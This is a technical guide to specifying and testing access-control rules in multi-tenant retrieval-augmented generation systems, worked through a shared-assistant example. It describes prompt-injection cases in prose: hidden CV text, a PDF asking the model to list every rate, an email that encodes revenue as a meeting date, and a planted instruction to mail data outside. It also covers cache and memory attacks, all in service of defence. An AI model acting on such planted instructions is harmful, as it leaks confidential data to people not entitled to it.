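# How to verify that security rules are enforced in retrieval-augmented generation systems

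## What it means for a rule to be enforced rather than written in a prompt

In retrieval-augmented generation (RAG), a program searches a collection of documents and passes what it finds, along with the user's question, to a large language model, which writes the answer. RAG lets the model answer from contracts, manuals and emails that were not in its training data. Mu, Hu and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Secure Retrieval-Augmented Generation*, trace the method to a 2020 proposal by Facebook's AI research group. Most such collections include documents that only some users may read, so RAG systems built on them need security rules. The most common rule is that no user receives text from a document they are not allowed to read. A developer can put this rule in the program code around the model or in the written instructions given to the model. Anyone verifying the rule needs to know which,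 because only the code can be checked without making assumptions about how the model will behave.

### One question on its way through the pipeline

Suppose a provider runs one assistant for two client firms, Alder and Birch. Each firm is a tenant, a customer whose data the provider must keep separate from that of other customers on the same system. Ana works at Alder, and the rule is that she must never receive text from Birch's files. Both firms use the same haulage company, but each negotiated its own contract. Ana asks the assistant, "What rate per pallet did the haulier agree for next year?"

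At intake, before she asks her question, the pipeline copies the files from each firm's storage and cuts them into chunks, passages of a few sentences or paragraphs that it will store and retrieve as units. Mu and colleagues explain that chunk size is a compromise, because a large chunk can bury the important point and a small one can cut a thought in half. An embedding model, separate from the model that writes answers, turns each chunk into an embedding, which is a list of numbers that represents the chunk's meaning. An index stores these numbers alongside the text.

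When the question arrives, the same embedding model turns it into a list of numbers *q*, and the search compares *q* with the list *c* of each stored chunk. A common measure is cosine similarity,

cos(*q*, *c*) = (*q* · *c*) / (‖*q*‖ ‖*c*‖),

which equals 1 when the two lists point in the same direction and 0 when they are at right angles. The search keeps the best-scoring chunks, and a reranker compares them with the question more finely and picks the final few. Next comes prompt assembly. Code joins the system prompt (the developer's standing instructions), the conversation so far, the question and the chosen chunks into a single text, the context. The model generates an answer from the context and the application displays it on Ana's screen. Xu, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *A Survey of Secure Retrieval-Augmented Generation*, divide the same path into six stages and give the delivery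 of the answer a stage of its own.

No step in this sequence depends on who Ana is. *Securing the Agent* (Arceo and Narsing, 2026) identifies this as the basic fault of RAG systems shared by several tenants: the search ranks text by relevance and ignores authorisation, so one tenant's confidential passage can appear in another's results simply because it scores highest. Suppose Birch's contract states its pallet rate in one plain sentence and scores 0.91, while Alder's contract gives the figure in a table and scores 0.84. Birch's rate then enters the context ahead of Alder's, although Ana asked an honest question about her own firm.

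### The same rule in two versions

A developer who notices the problem might add this instruction to the system prompt: "The user works for Alder. Never reveal anything from Birch's files." This rule is only represented in the prompt, because the search hasn't changed. Birch's rate still enters the context, and keeping it from Ana depends on the model following the instruction.

The alternative is to change the search. The login service establishes that Ana belongs to Alder, and the retrieval code attaches a condition to every search it runs:

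`search(vector = q, limit = 5, where tenant = session.tenant)`

The value of `session.tenant` comes from the login, so neither Ana's input nor the model's output can change it. Birch's chunk is no longer a candidate, whatever its score. This is pre-filtering, which applies the access rule before or during the search. Post-filtering searches everything and then removes the forbidden results. Both can keep Birch's text out of the context, as long as post-filtering removes it before the prompt is assembled. They differ in the resources they use and the number of results they return. For example, if Birch's chunks take all five places, post-filtering leaves Ana with no results.

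The prompt sentence is weak because a language model has no separate channels for instructions and data, as David C explains in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre. The model receives one run of tokens (words and fragments of words) and predicts the next. Ana's question, the haulage contract and the developer's sentence about Birch are all part of that run, and no mechanism makes the model obey the developer's sentence.

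Prompt injection exploits this. The term covers any text in a question or document that the model treats as an instruction. For example, Ana could type that the two firms merged this morning and the restriction has lapsed. The attacker does not have to be a user. David C describes a job applicant who hides a line in a CV telling the screening model to approve it. In the haulage example, a supplier's PDF in Alder's own folder might contain a line asking the model to list every rate it can see, and Ana would receive Birch's figure without trying to get it.

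Prompt injection looks similar to SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into a web form and the database runs them. Parameterised queries fixed SQL injection by passing the form's contents to the database in a way that prevents them from being executed. David C doubts that prompt injection will ever have a similar fix. Developers can mark outside text as data or train a model to prioritise their instructions. Both methods lower the failure rate, which attack tests can measure, but neither enforces a boundary between instructions and data.

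### The hostile-model assumption

The difference between the two versions suggests a general criterion. A rule is enforced if it would still hold after the model was replaced with a program that an attacker wrote. The program receives the same context as the model, and its output goes wherever the model's output would have gone. In symbols, let *C* be the context that the pipeline builds for Ana, and let *M* be any program that takes *C* and returns an output. The rule is enforced if no choice of *M* gets Birch's text to Ana.

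One counterexample is enough to show that the prompt version does not enforce the rule. If *M* prints *C* in full, the rule is broken. In the filtered version, the same program prints Alder's chunks and the system prompt. No other program can extract Birch's data from *C* either, because *C* contains none of it.

Treating the model as an adversary makes sense even though a commercial model follows its instructions most of the time, because an attacker whose injection succeeds controls the output for that answer, and the rule exists for that case. It also means the tester doesn't have to predict what the model will do. In *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026) make the same assumption when they build a monitor for agents (models that take actions through software tools). They treat the agent as an untrusted component that may attempt anything,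 so they don't need to explain why it tried to send a particular email. *Agent libOS* (2026) likewise assumes an adversary who controls both the retrieved documents and the model's output. The argument for the filter also still holds when the provider switches to a new model, whereas the provider has to test a prompted rule again from the beginning.

Some rules that look enforced fail this criterion. In many newer systems, the model decides when to search and writes the search request. If the search tool has a `tenant` field that the model fills in, the attacker's program writes "Birch" there. The filter runs in code on every search, but the rule still fails because the untrusted part of the system supplies the value that the filter checks. The argument also assumes that the program has no other source of Birch's text, such as a memory that carries over between users or a model that the provider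 trained on both firms' files.

A rule against revealing text cannot be fully enforced if the model has that text in its context. Xu and colleagues define protected knowledge as stored content that may support an answer but that the system must not reveal beyond what a policy allows. For example, Birch might let the assistant consult its contracts to tell Alder whether a clause is unusual, on condition that it never quotes them. The model would then need Birch's contract in its context, and a hostile program in the model's place could print it. An output filter would catch a direct copy, but not one written in cipher or spelled out in the first letters of a harmless paragraph. The designers can either accept that the rule depends partly on the model's behavior, and record that, or have separate code compare the clauses and pass only a yes or no into the context.

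### The reference monitor and the trusted computing base

The idea of planning for a hostile program inside the system is more than fifty years old. The US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) reported what a panel of specialists thought this would take. The panel planned for a malicious user with a legitimate account who could run their own programs. It proposed a reference monitor, a mechanism that checks every attempt by any program to reach data, a device or another program against a list of what the program's user may do. The list is in effect a table with a row for each user and a column for each resource. Ana's row would have "read" under Alder's files and an empty cell under Birch's.

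Anderson set three requirements for the mechanism. It must be tamper-proof, and the system must always invoke it. It must also be small enough to analyse and test completely, because otherwise nobody can know whether it meets the first two requirements.

The report applied these to a computer of the time, the HIS 635 running the GCOS III operating system. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory, which is a kind of reference monitor. But most of the operating system ran in a mode that suspended this confinement, even when doing work for a user, so the check did not always apply. If the operating system itself is counted as the monitor, then the monitor had 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, far too many to verify, and teams of testers had already broken into it several times.

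*Ring-0 by Default* (Li, Huang and colleagues, 2026) concludes that rules in a prompt meet none of Anderson's requirements. The sentence about Birch, for example, fails because the model may not apply it to a given answer, any other text in the context can contradict it, and verifying it would require analysing the entire model.

The search filter does better but does not qualify automatically. It is always invoked only if every route by which text reaches the context goes through it. Li and colleagues tested three coding agents (Claude Code, Codex CLI and Gemini CLI) and found that access checks were inside individual tools, so a file write blocked by the file tool succeeded through the command shell. The equivalent in a RAG system would be filtering the embedding search but not the keyword search beside it. Size is also a problem because, although the condition is one line, the team also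 has to rely on the large database software that applies it.

The trusted computing base is the set of parts that must work correctly for a rule to hold. "Trusted" means that the rule fails if the part fails, not that the part is reliable. Recent agent designs include different parts in this base. *Kairos* (2026) includes only an isolation layer, a monitor and the host machine, and treats everything else, including the model, as untrusted. *Agent libOS* has a much longer list, which includes the Python interpreter, the storage system, the operating system and the human operator when approving a request.

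For Ana's rule, the base contains the login service, the code that passes her tenant to the search, the database, the machine it runs on, and the intake step that labels each chunk with its owner. The intake step is easy to forget, but if someone saves Birch's contract in Alder's folder, intake labels it as Alder's and a correctly working filter returns it to Ana. The answering model, the documents and the question are outside the base. The embedding model is also outside it for this rule, because a bad one gives Ana a poor choice of Alder's chunks but still none of Birch's.

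### OWASP's advice on system prompts

The Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit that publishes ranked lists of software risks, reached the same position in its 2025 list for language-model applications. *LLM07:2025 System Prompt Leakage* mainly argues that a system prompt is neither a secret nor a security control, and it also advises developers to keep passwords and keys out of the prompt. If a leaked prompt contains roles and permissions, OWASP considers the real fault to be that the application left authorisation to the model. One of its sample prompts tells the model to refuse any request for information about another user, which is almost the same as the sentence about Birch. An attacker can work out much of such a prompt by watching which questions the model declines. OWASP wants authorisation checks to run outside the model and to be deterministic and auditable.

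OWASP (2026) released a newer edition on August 3, 2026. The entry is now called Hidden Context Exposure and, according to Real Python's *OWASP LLM Top 10*, covers any behind-the-scenes text that an attacker can read back. According to SC Media's *OWASP updates top 10 security risks for LLM applications*, developers should assume that attackers can discover hidden context, and should not make it the sole control for authorisation. This is milder than the 2025 wording because "sole" allows a prompt sentence as an extra layer, which does no harm as long as the filter passes the hostile-model test without it.

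Prompt injection would not make the new edition's top ten if OWASP ranked by recorded incidents alone, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* (2026). Practitioners rank it first, and OWASP says few clear cases become public because teams work hard to prevent them. That may be right, but the count would also be low if attacks were rare. The case for enforcement is the same either way, because it rests on the absence of a boundary inside the model. OWASP itself advises designing systems on the assumption that attackers will eventually get past the model's instructions.

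### Three grades of evidence

A claim that the filter works can rest on tests, on a bound that holds under stated conditions, or on a formal proof.

A test can show that a rule is not enforced by producing a leak, but a test that finds no leaks covers only the cases tried. Anderson made this point about the "tiger teams" of the time, experts who attacked a system to see whether it would hold. When such a team fails, all one can conclude is that the system's security is unknown. The same limit applies to Arceo and Narsing's evaluation, in which a retrieval-time check comparing user and document attributes eliminated leakage between tenants with negligible overhead. Such a result is stronger evidence for a filter than for a prompt, because a filter applies the same short condition to every question, whereas a model's response can change with the wording.

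A bound is a mathematical guarantee that holds only up to a stated limit. Xu and colleagues cite RobustRAG, a defence against planted documents that processes the retrieved passages and combines the resulting outputs. Its guarantee covers a fixed question and a limited amount of corruption among the passages. The guarantee doesn't apply if an attacker exceeds that limit, so relying on it requires good reasons to think that no attacker can.

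A formal proof covers every possible run of a mathematical description of the system, not of the system itself. Anderson therefore asked for two things before anyone certified a machine: a proof that the description is secure, and a demonstration that the built system matches it. The second is still the difficult part. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) offers theorems about defences for agents that apply only to systems satisfying seven assumptions. One is that the model reaches tools and untrusted sources only through the monitor. Another is that outsiders cannot write to any source the system trusts, so a calendar that accepts invitations from strangers cannot be a trusted source. Palumbo and colleagues add that their guarantee does not cover cases where the policy itself permits something unsafe. Similarly, a proof about the Alder and Birch filter could show that Ana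 receives only chunks labelled "Alder", but someone would still have to check that the labels are right.

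## State the rule as a property that can fail a test

"Ana must not see Birch's data" is too vague to test. Suppose Birch's pallet rate enters the context but the model leaves it out of the answer. Testers might disagree about whether that is a breach. They might also disagree about a reply that contains none of Birch's text but mentions that three hidden documents matched Ana's question. *SoK* (Bodea, Meisenbacher and colleagues, 2026) reviewed 72 papers on privacy in RAG and found that many discuss leakage but few state explicitly which form they protect against.

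Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, proposed four steps for avoiding this: finding out what security the system's users need, writing that need as a formal requirement, describing the system, and showing that the description meets the requirement. Only the last step is purely mathematical. For the assistant that Alder and Birch share, the second step produces five properties, (a) to (e).

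### (a) The user may read every chunk in the context

Write *C*(*u*, *t*) for the context that the pipeline builds for user *u* at time *t*, and may(*u*, *c*, *t*) for "the permission table lets *u* read chunk *c* at time *t*". Context authorisation is then

for every chunk *c* in *C*(*u*, *t*): may(*u*, *c*, *t*).

"Chunk" has to include text derived from documents. Ana may receive a summary only if she may read every document that went into it.

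Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, define access control in the same way for systems in general. They describe a run as a trace, the sequence of states the system passes through. Whenever someone carries out an operation, the access table in the state just before it must contain the rights the operation needs. A complete log of one run is therefore enough to decide whether that run obeyed the rule. A breach shows up after a finite time and nothing later can undo it, so the system has failed if even one log has a Birch chunk in Ana's context.

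The tester logs each context, looks up who may read each chunk, and fails the system at the first chunk the user may not read, without needing to read the model's answers. *Isolation Is Not Confidentiality* (Nouyep, Puys and Salva, 2026) uses two rates to measure how badly a system fails. The query violation rate is the share of queries that return at least one unauthorised document, and the unauthorised chunk rate is the share of retrieved chunks that are unauthorised. Suppose a tester asks 200 questions that retrieve five chunks each, and three of the questions bring in one Birch chunk each. The query violation rate is 3/200, or 1.5%, and the unauthorised chunk rate is 3/1,000, or 0.3%. A security invariant, meaning a rule that must hold in every run, requires both to be zero. The paper calculates the rates on search results, but for property (a) they should be calculated on the finished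 context, since a post-filter may remove forbidden results before the model receives them.

### (b) Every recipient may read every chunk

Property (a) is too weak when other people will read the answer. Suppose Ana and Ben, who works at Birch, plan a joint shipment in a group chat that includes the assistant. Ana asks a question, the search finds a confidential Alder memo that she may read, and the answer appears on Ben's screen. Let *R* be everyone who will receive the answer. The stricter property is

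for every chunk *c* in the context and every recipient *r* in *R*: may(*r*, *c*, *t*).

In *Position*, Bhatt, Rajore and colleagues at Microsoft (2025) argue for this rule, which they call participant-aware access control. They describe an attack on an email assistant in which Bob emails Alice to suggest a meeting. Hidden text in the email instructs the model to look up Project X's revenue and propose the day of the month that matches the figure in millions. When Alice asks her assistant to draft a reply, it searches her mailbox, finds that the revenue is $7 million, and proposes 7 May. Alice sees nothing odd and sends the reply, which reveals the revenue to Bob.

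Property (a) holds throughout, because Alice may read everything in her own mailbox. Bhatt and colleagues argue that no inspection of the request could reliably have caught the attack, since Alice's manager might legitimately ask for the same figure. Whether the answer is allowed depends on who receives it. An output filter is also unlikely to catch the attack, because a meeting date looks harmless. Bhatt and colleagues therefore want the system to check the permissions of everyone involved before it gives any content to the model. If Bob copies in Charlie, the check includes Charlie. For a shared document, it includes everyone with read access.

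When a document fails the check, an assistant that sends mail by itself must leave it out. An assistant that shows Alice a draft first may instead ask for her consent to use the revenue message in a reply to Bob. Her approval of the finished draft is not enough, because it covers only the sentence about 7 May and not the use of the revenue message.

The rule limits what the assistant can use. In the chat between Ana and Ben, it may draw only on documents that both can read, which might be little more than the haulier's public price list. Retrieving more and letting the model judge what suits the audience can leak private information. *MuPPET* (Ruzzetti, Emde and colleagues, 2026) tested how well models make this judgement in 562 synthetic workplace conversations, where an assistant held private notes about the employee it spoke for. In one comparison, the prompt also stated what the employee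 did not want to share and with whom. GPT-5.5 leaked private information in 14.22% of one-to-one conversations and 26.71% of group conversations. Gemini 2.5 Pro did so in 9.88% and 23.46%. Llama 3.1 8B was the only one of the seven models that did not get worse in groups, and it leaked in about 60% of cases in both settings.

Newer models may do better, but the task grows with the number of recipients. With *N* recipients and *K* private items, all *N* × *K* combinations have to be appropriate. Code only has to look up more table entries. *Multi-User Large Language Model Agents* (2026) likewise treats access as a hard constraint. The agent weighs its users' requests by priority, but only among actions the access policy allows, so a request from Ana's managing director cannot override Birch's permissions.

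### (c) Forbidden documents make no difference

Noninterference is a stronger property than (a). It requires that changing data a user may not read changes nothing that the user can observe. Goguen and Meseguer define it by deleting commands from a system's history. Let *w* be a sequence of commands, each marked with the user who gave it, and let *p*(*w*) be the same sequence without the commands of a group *G*. Write *w*ᵤ for what user *u* sees after *w*. Then *G* does not interfere with *u* if

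*w*ᵤ = *p*(*w*)ᵤ for every *w*.

Suppose Birch and Alder each upload a contract, and then Ana asks her question. If someone deletes Birch's upload and replays the other steps, Ana must see the same screen. Goguen and Meseguer give the example of a file that does not exist at the start. If the commands that create, change or delete it must not affect *u*, then the system must always report to *u* that the file doesn't exist, whatever other people have done. By this standard, the message "You do not have permission to open Birch's contract" is a breach, because it reveals that the contract exists.

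Their definition assumes a deterministic machine, whereas a language model usually picks its words partly at random and can answer the same question differently each time. The RAG version therefore compares probabilities. Let *D* and *D*′ be two document stores that differ only in documents *u* may not read. For every such pair, every series of questions *q* and every possible observation *o*,

Pr[*u* observes *o* | *D*, *q*] = Pr[*u* observes *o* | *D*′, *q*].

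A rule that only requires the same observations to be possible with both stores can still let secrets leak. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that outputs 0, 1 or the value of a secret bit. Both outputs are possible whatever the secret is. But if the system chooses among the three options with equal probability and the secret is 1, it outputs 1 two times in three, so anyone who can repeat the query will soon guess the secret.

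A tester cannot tell from the log of a single run that (c) has failed, because (c) concerns what Ana would have seen if the forbidden documents had been different. Clarkson and Schneider call a requirement on a system's whole set of runs a hyperproperty. They prove that if two finite runs are always enough to expose a breach, the requirement is equivalent to an ordinary single-run property of two copies of the system running side by side. A tester can therefore set up two copies of the pipeline with the same Alder files, change or remove Birch's files in one copy, ask both the same questions and compare the results.

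Two answers to the same question may differ by chance, so the tester can repeat each question many times and compare frequencies. Alternatively, the hostile-model assumption lets the tester replace the model with a program that prints its whole context. Property (c) can then hold only if the context has the same distribution with both stores. The tester can therefore compare contexts, which vary much less than answers because ordinary code builds them. Ana also observes things outside the context, such as the list of sources, error messages and response times, and these need their own checks.

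### Five results, three of them forbidden

A system can satisfy (a) and still fail (c). Suppose the search always returns the five best chunks, and a post-filter then removes any that Ana is not allowed to read.

| | Birch's files in the store | Birch's files removed |
|---|---|---|
| Search returns | 2 Alder chunks, 3 Birch chunks | 5 Alder chunks |
| Filter removes | 3 | 0 |
| Ana's context | 2 Alder chunks | 5 Alder chunks |

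Ana may read every chunk in both contexts, so (a) holds in both columns. But the contexts differ, and Ana can count the sources if the application lists them. She knows that Alder has dozens of files on haulage, so a list of two suggests that three documents she can't see matched her question better. She could ask about penalties for late delivery to Rotterdam, or about a rumoured merger, and see how the count changes. Each count has six possible values, from 0 to 5, so it can reveal up to log₂ 6 ≈ 2.6 bits about other people's files. A pre-filter that returns the five best Alder chunks in both cases removes this difference.

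Under the hostile-model assumption, (c) does imply (a). If a Birch chunk is in Ana's context, deleting Birch's files changes that context, unless Alder's files contain the same passage.

Nouyep and colleagues found a similar gap in systems where a trusted server separates tenants by applying a secret transformation to each tenant's embeddings. A question transformed for one tenant then scores poorly against another tenant's chunks. The systems they tested kept unauthorised documents out of the search results well, but someone with access to the stored embeddings could still infer which policy a document belonged to. A user who had a few hundred pairs of original and transformed embeddings could also recover other original embeddings. To get those pairs for someone else's files, the user would need the database provider's help, so this attack requires much more than asking questions.

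Strict noninterference also rules out some useful services, such as the code that compares contract clauses for Alder, because its yes-or-no answer depends on Birch's contracts. Goguen and Meseguer allow for such services with a rule that two groups may affect each other only through a named set of commands. The specification can name the clause comparison as the one permitted channel and apply (c) to everything else.

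### (d) Untrusted text does not choose actions

Assistants that can send emails or change records need a property for actions as well. Let *T* be the trusted input, such as Ana's request and the developer's instructions, and let *X* be the untrusted text, such as retrieved documents and incoming mail. Write Act(*T*, *X*) for the actions that the system carries out, including their arguments (the recipient of an email, for example). The integrity property is

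Act(*T*, *X*) = Act(*T*, *X*′) for every *T*, *X* and *X*′,

or equal probabilities where the model's output is random. This is noninterference applied to influence: changing the untrusted text must not change what the system does. It also takes two runs to test. In one, the supplier's PDF in Alder's folder is clean. In the other, it contains a line telling the assistant to email every rate to an outside address. If the assistant sends that email only in the second run, (d) has failed.

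The strict form would block much ordinary work. If Ana asks the assistant to send the haulier a note confirming next year's rate, the rate has to come from the contract. A practical specification therefore lists the arguments that untrusted text may fill, which might include the body of the email but never the recipient. This exception still needs (b), because in the 7 May attack Bob received the revenue figure through the body of a message that Alice had asked for. With label tracking, in which code marks each value with its source, testers can check a single run.

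### (e) Access ends within a stated time

Suppose Birch lets Ana read one contract for a joint bid and withdraws permission at noon on Friday. Goguen and Meseguer model withdrawal as a command that takes effect before the user's next command. RAG pipelines often copy permissions into the search index, and the copy may be out of date. Let granted(*u*, *c*, *s*) mean that the owner's own records allowed *u* to read *c* at time *s*, and let Δ be the longest delay that the owner will accept. The revocation property is

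for every chunk *c* in *C*(*u*, *t*), there is a time *s* between *t* − Δ and *t* at which granted(*u*, *c*, *s*).

If Δ is 15 minutes, the contract may still appear in Ana's context at 12:10 but not at 12:16. One log with timestamps and Birch's record of permissions are enough for the test. A promise that access will end "eventually" can't fail any test, because however long the tester waits, access might still end later.

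The property covers the whole context, including the conversation history. If Ana asked about the contract on Friday morning, a follow-up question at three o'clock could send the same passage to the model again, even though the search no longer returns it. The provider would have to remove the passage from the history too.

### Refusing, not retrieving and not disclosing

Developers often support a claim of protection with evidence for a different claim. Suppose Ana asks for Birch's rate and the assistant replies that it can't help. This shows only that the assistant refused, since Birch's contract may still have been in its context. If the log lists no Birch chunks among the search results, then the search did not retrieve the contract, but the rate might still have reached the model through a saved conversation. Even if the answer doesn't contain the rate, a differently worded question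 might reveal it.

Liu, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Protection Is Not One Event*, surveyed 118 papers on RAG defences and sorted them by what their experiments measured. Only 21 (17.8%) primarily measured whether protected content reached a user or whether an attacker could reconstruct it. Another 26 measured whether the system blocked retrieval or declined to answer, and 96% of those reported an improvement. These results don't show that the defences prevent disclosure. For instance, some methods for making a system "forget" documents count as successful if the system refuses questions about them, even if the content is still there.

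Liu and colleagues also ran an experiment in which the model could use certain documents but not quote them. An output filter removed any run of eight words that matched a protected source. Copying of 20-token passages fell to 0.0%. But an attacker who could ask three questions, adapting each to the previous replies, still recovered 48.3% of the hidden facts from the model Qwen3-8B, compared with 3.3% after one question. Ana's rule has to protect the facts, because revealing Birch's pallet rate is just as damaging in new words. Whoever writes a disclosure test must therefore specify whether it checks for wording or facts, and how many questions the attacker may ask.

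In the same experiment, filtering before retrieval worked when the labels were complete. But when 12.5% of the labels were missing and the system treated unlabelled documents as open to everyone, the model again copied protected text verbatim in 9.4% to 12.5% of cases. A specification that doesn't mention labels would miss this failure.

### A sample specification

Goguen and Meseguer state that their method does not cover user authentication, faults, or conclusions that people draw from information they are allowed to see. A RAG specification has similar limits and should list them beside its rules. A specification for the shared assistant might read as follows.

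1. Every recipient of an answer may read every passage in the context behind it, including summaries, saved memories and earlier messages. One logged context with a forbidden passage fails this rule.
2. For the same questions, two copies of the system that differ only in documents the user may not read produce the same contexts, source lists and error messages. A difference that recurs when the tester repeats the comparison fails this rule. The clause comparison is exempt and may return one yes or no per request.
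3. Text from documents and incoming mail may fill the body of a message that the user asked for. It may not choose the tool, the recipient or the attachments. One action that changes in any of these respects when only the untrusted text changes fails this rule.
4. No passage enters a context more than 15 minutes after its owner withdraws permission. Answers that the user has already read are outside this rule.

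The rules hold under these assumptions:

- The login service identifies each user correctly, and the list of recipients includes everyone who can open the conversation later.
- Intake gives every document the right owner. The system treats a passage without a label as forbidden to everyone.
- The permission records match what Alder and Birch have agreed.
- The provider has not trained the model on either firm's files, and the model receives nothing beyond the logged context.
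- The logs contain every context and action in full, with accurate times.
- Separate tests cover response time, which rule 2 leaves out.
- Nobody at Birch passes the text to Ana by other means.

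## Find every path by which text reaches the model

The sample specification requires that every recipient of an answer be allowed to read every passage in the context used to generate it. A tenant filter on the vector search guarantees this only for the passages that search returns. The context also includes the conversation so far, and many pipelines add keyword matches, tool output and text from the user's open files. If text from any of these sources isn't checked, Ana can receive Birch's pallet rate even when the filter works correctly.

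The relevant principle is complete mediation, which *Saltzer and Schroeder Principles*, a web page of extracts from a 1975 paper on protecting information in computers, states as "Every access to every object must be checked for authority." Anderson had already required the same thing by insisting that the system always invoke the reference monitor. Verifying this takes a list of every path to the model as well as tests of the check, because a test of the vector search doesn't cover a path that nobody has listed.

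### A label rule that missed two mail folders

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers questions from an organisation's emails, documents and chats. Administrators can label items "Confidential" and set a data loss prevention (DLP) rule that stops Copilot from processing anything with that label. Microsoft (2025) announced in June 2025 that it would extend these rules to emails as well as files.

In early 2026 the rule failed for two folders. The advisory, numbered CW1226324 and quoted in Office365ITPros' *Code Error Allowed Copilot Chat to Expose Confidential Information* (2026), blamed a "code issue" that let Copilot pick up labelled items in Sent Items and Drafts. Other folders seemed unaffected, although TechRadar's *Microsoft admits an Office bug exposed confidential user emails to Copilot* pointed out that threads in those two folders presumably include incoming emails. Office365ITPros and a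 news report, The Stack's *28 days later copilot is probably not ingesting confidential email anymore*, give these dates:

- **21 January 2026:** Customers first reported the problem, according to Office365ITPros. The Stack found it unclear whether the date marks the first reports or the update that broke the rule.
- **3 February:** Microsoft issued the advisory. Within three hours of logging the problem, it had identified the code error and begun to deploy a fix.
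- **10 February:** Microsoft said the fix was still spreading across its servers.
- **About 17 February:** The news site BleepingComputer reported the bug, which had gone largely unnoticed until then.
- **18 February:** Microsoft was contacting some of the affected users.
- **19 February:** Microsoft said some users had confirmed that the fix worked. It expected to finish by its next update, due on 24 February.

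Microsoft says nobody gained access to information they were not already authorised to see. The user had written the emails, which were in the user's own folders. Microsoft accepted that Copilot should have excluded them. On this account, the system enforced the rule about who may read an email but not the separate rule about what Copilot may process. Microsoft did not reply when The Stack asked whether sensitive information had crossed boundaries inside organisations.

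The first rule also protects less when the permissions behind it are too broad. John (2026) reports in *A viral TikTok about Copilot leaking layoffs is a joke* that security experts worry about how much information Copilot users already have permission to see.

The labels and the policy were correct, and the check apparently worked in other folders. After the fix, Office365ITPros tested the rule by sending a labelled message about a fictitious "Project Bunny". Copilot found the message but did not disclose its contents. The site remarked that sent mail is an obvious place to test, and a labelled test message in each folder would probably have exposed the bug.

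Some gaps in the same rule were already public. According to Microsoft's documentation, the rule covers emails sent since the start of 2025 but not calendar invitations, and DLP cannot scan files a user uploads into a prompt. The documentation also says that the rule covers only files stored in SharePoint Online or OneDrive, two Microsoft storage services. A notice reproduced in itelio's *DLP policies will be able to block Copilot processing of sensitivity‑labeled files* explains that the software looked up a file's label through its SharePoint or OneDrive address, so it could not look up the label of a file on a laptop. In April 2026 Microsoft (2026) was rolling out a version for Word, Excel and PowerPoint that works wherever the file is stored. In this version, the Office program supplies the label itself, which adds that program to the trusted computing base.

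### How to list the paths

A tester with access to the code can build an inventory in five steps.

1. Start at the model and work backwards. Find every place where the code calls a model, including minor calls that rewrite the question or summarise a long conversation. Trace each piece of text in the call to the store or person it came from.
2. Start at Birch's documents and work forwards. List every copy the system makes, such as indexes, caches, previews and summaries, and find every program that reads each copy.
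3. List every way a user can send a request: the chat window, the search box, the mobile app, the email add-in and any programming interface. Two of these may reach the same index through different code.
4. For each path, name the enforcement point, which is the place in the code where a check can refuse the read. Record where the check gets the user's identity and the document's label, and what it does if either is missing. A path whose only protection is a sentence in the prompt has a gap.
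5. Compare the inventory with logged contexts. The log should record which path supplied each passage. A passage with no recorded path means that either the logging is faulty or the inventory is incomplete.

Steps 1 and 2 overlap, but each finds things the other misses. For example, working backwards from the model does not find a cached answer that goes straight to the user's screen.

For the assistant that Alder and Birch share, the inventory might look like this:

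| Path | How Birch's text could reach Ana | Enforcement point or gap |
|---|---|---|
| Vector search | Birch's contract outscores Alder's | Enforced: retrieval code adds the tenant from Ana's login |
| Keyword search | Ana searches for the haulier's name | Enforced: the same condition applies to the keyword index |
| Graph expansion | The haulier's name links the two firms' contracts | **Gap:** no check after the first search |
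| Answer cache | Ben of Birch asked the same question an hour ago | **Gap:** the cache compares questions but not tenants |
| Conversation memory | Ana asked about a Birch contract before Birch withdrew permission | **Gap:** code resends old messages without a new check |
| Tool results | A tool opens a file by its number | Enforced: the tool uses Ana's login, so the file server refuses |
| File previews | Ana pastes a link and the application fetches the first page | **Gap:** the preview service uses an administrator account |
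| Search box | A search page summarises its results with the same model | **Gap:** the page queries the index through older, unfiltered code |

Five of the eight paths have gaps, and a test of the vector search would find none of them.

### Caches and other copies

A semantic cache stores past answers with the embeddings of their questions. When a new question is similar enough to an old one, the application returns the old answer without calling the model. If Ben asks for the haulier's pallet rate at ten and Ana asks the same question at eleven, she gets Birch's figure. The context log shows nothing wrong, because the pipeline never built a context for her.

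*Local-Splitter* (2026), a study of ways to reduce the cost of coding assistants, keeps separate cache entries for each workspace and gives them an expiry time to avoid out-of-date answers. Separating entries by tenant would also stop the cache from passing text between Alder and Birch. If colleagues within a firm have different permissions, the cache must be divided more finely. An expiry time of more than 15 minutes could also break the specification's rule on withdrawn permission.

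An attacker can exploit a shared cache deliberately. *From Similarity to Vulnerability* (2026) explains that a semantic cache must accept near matches to be useful, which lets an attacker craft a question whose stored answer later goes to someone else. *LaCache* (Liang, Wang and colleagues, 2026) proposes a defence that also requires a match on the first few tokens of a freshly generated response. This reduced the attack's hit rate to near zero and preserved over 90% of the cache's usefulness. But the defence is designed to stop corrupted answers, so it would not reliably stop the leak from Ben to Ana, where the stored answer is a genuine reply to the same question.

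The search index is a copy too, and it can outlast the original. In *ConfusedPilot*, RoyChowdhury, Luo and colleagues (2024) deleted documents and kept asking Copilot for Microsoft 365 about them. Copilot continued to use an ordinary document for about 164 seconds after its deletion, and for about 183 seconds when the researchers removed only the relevant text from the file. In one example, the answer cited a link that no longer worked. The researchers warned that if an owner shared a confidential file by mistake and withdrew access before anyone opened it, Copilot could still reveal the contents from its index. A three-minute delay would satisfy the 15-minute limit in the sample specification, but the researchers tested one product in 2024, and the delay in another system depends on how often it updates its index.

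Documents that the assistant writes also count as copies, because a later search may retrieve them. Kusenberg (2026), in *Copilot Created the Document*, reports that since July 2026, files that Copilot generates have inherited the highest sensitivity label among their sources. This works for ranked labels, but "Alder" and "Birch" have no ranking, so a report that draws on both firms' files needs the specification's rule for summaries instead.

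### Memory, tools and secondary interfaces

Code has to check permissions again whenever it resends old text from memory to the model. Checking only each new question is not enough, because *FragFuse* (2026) describes an attack that splits a forbidden request into fragments and uses the agent's memory to put them together.

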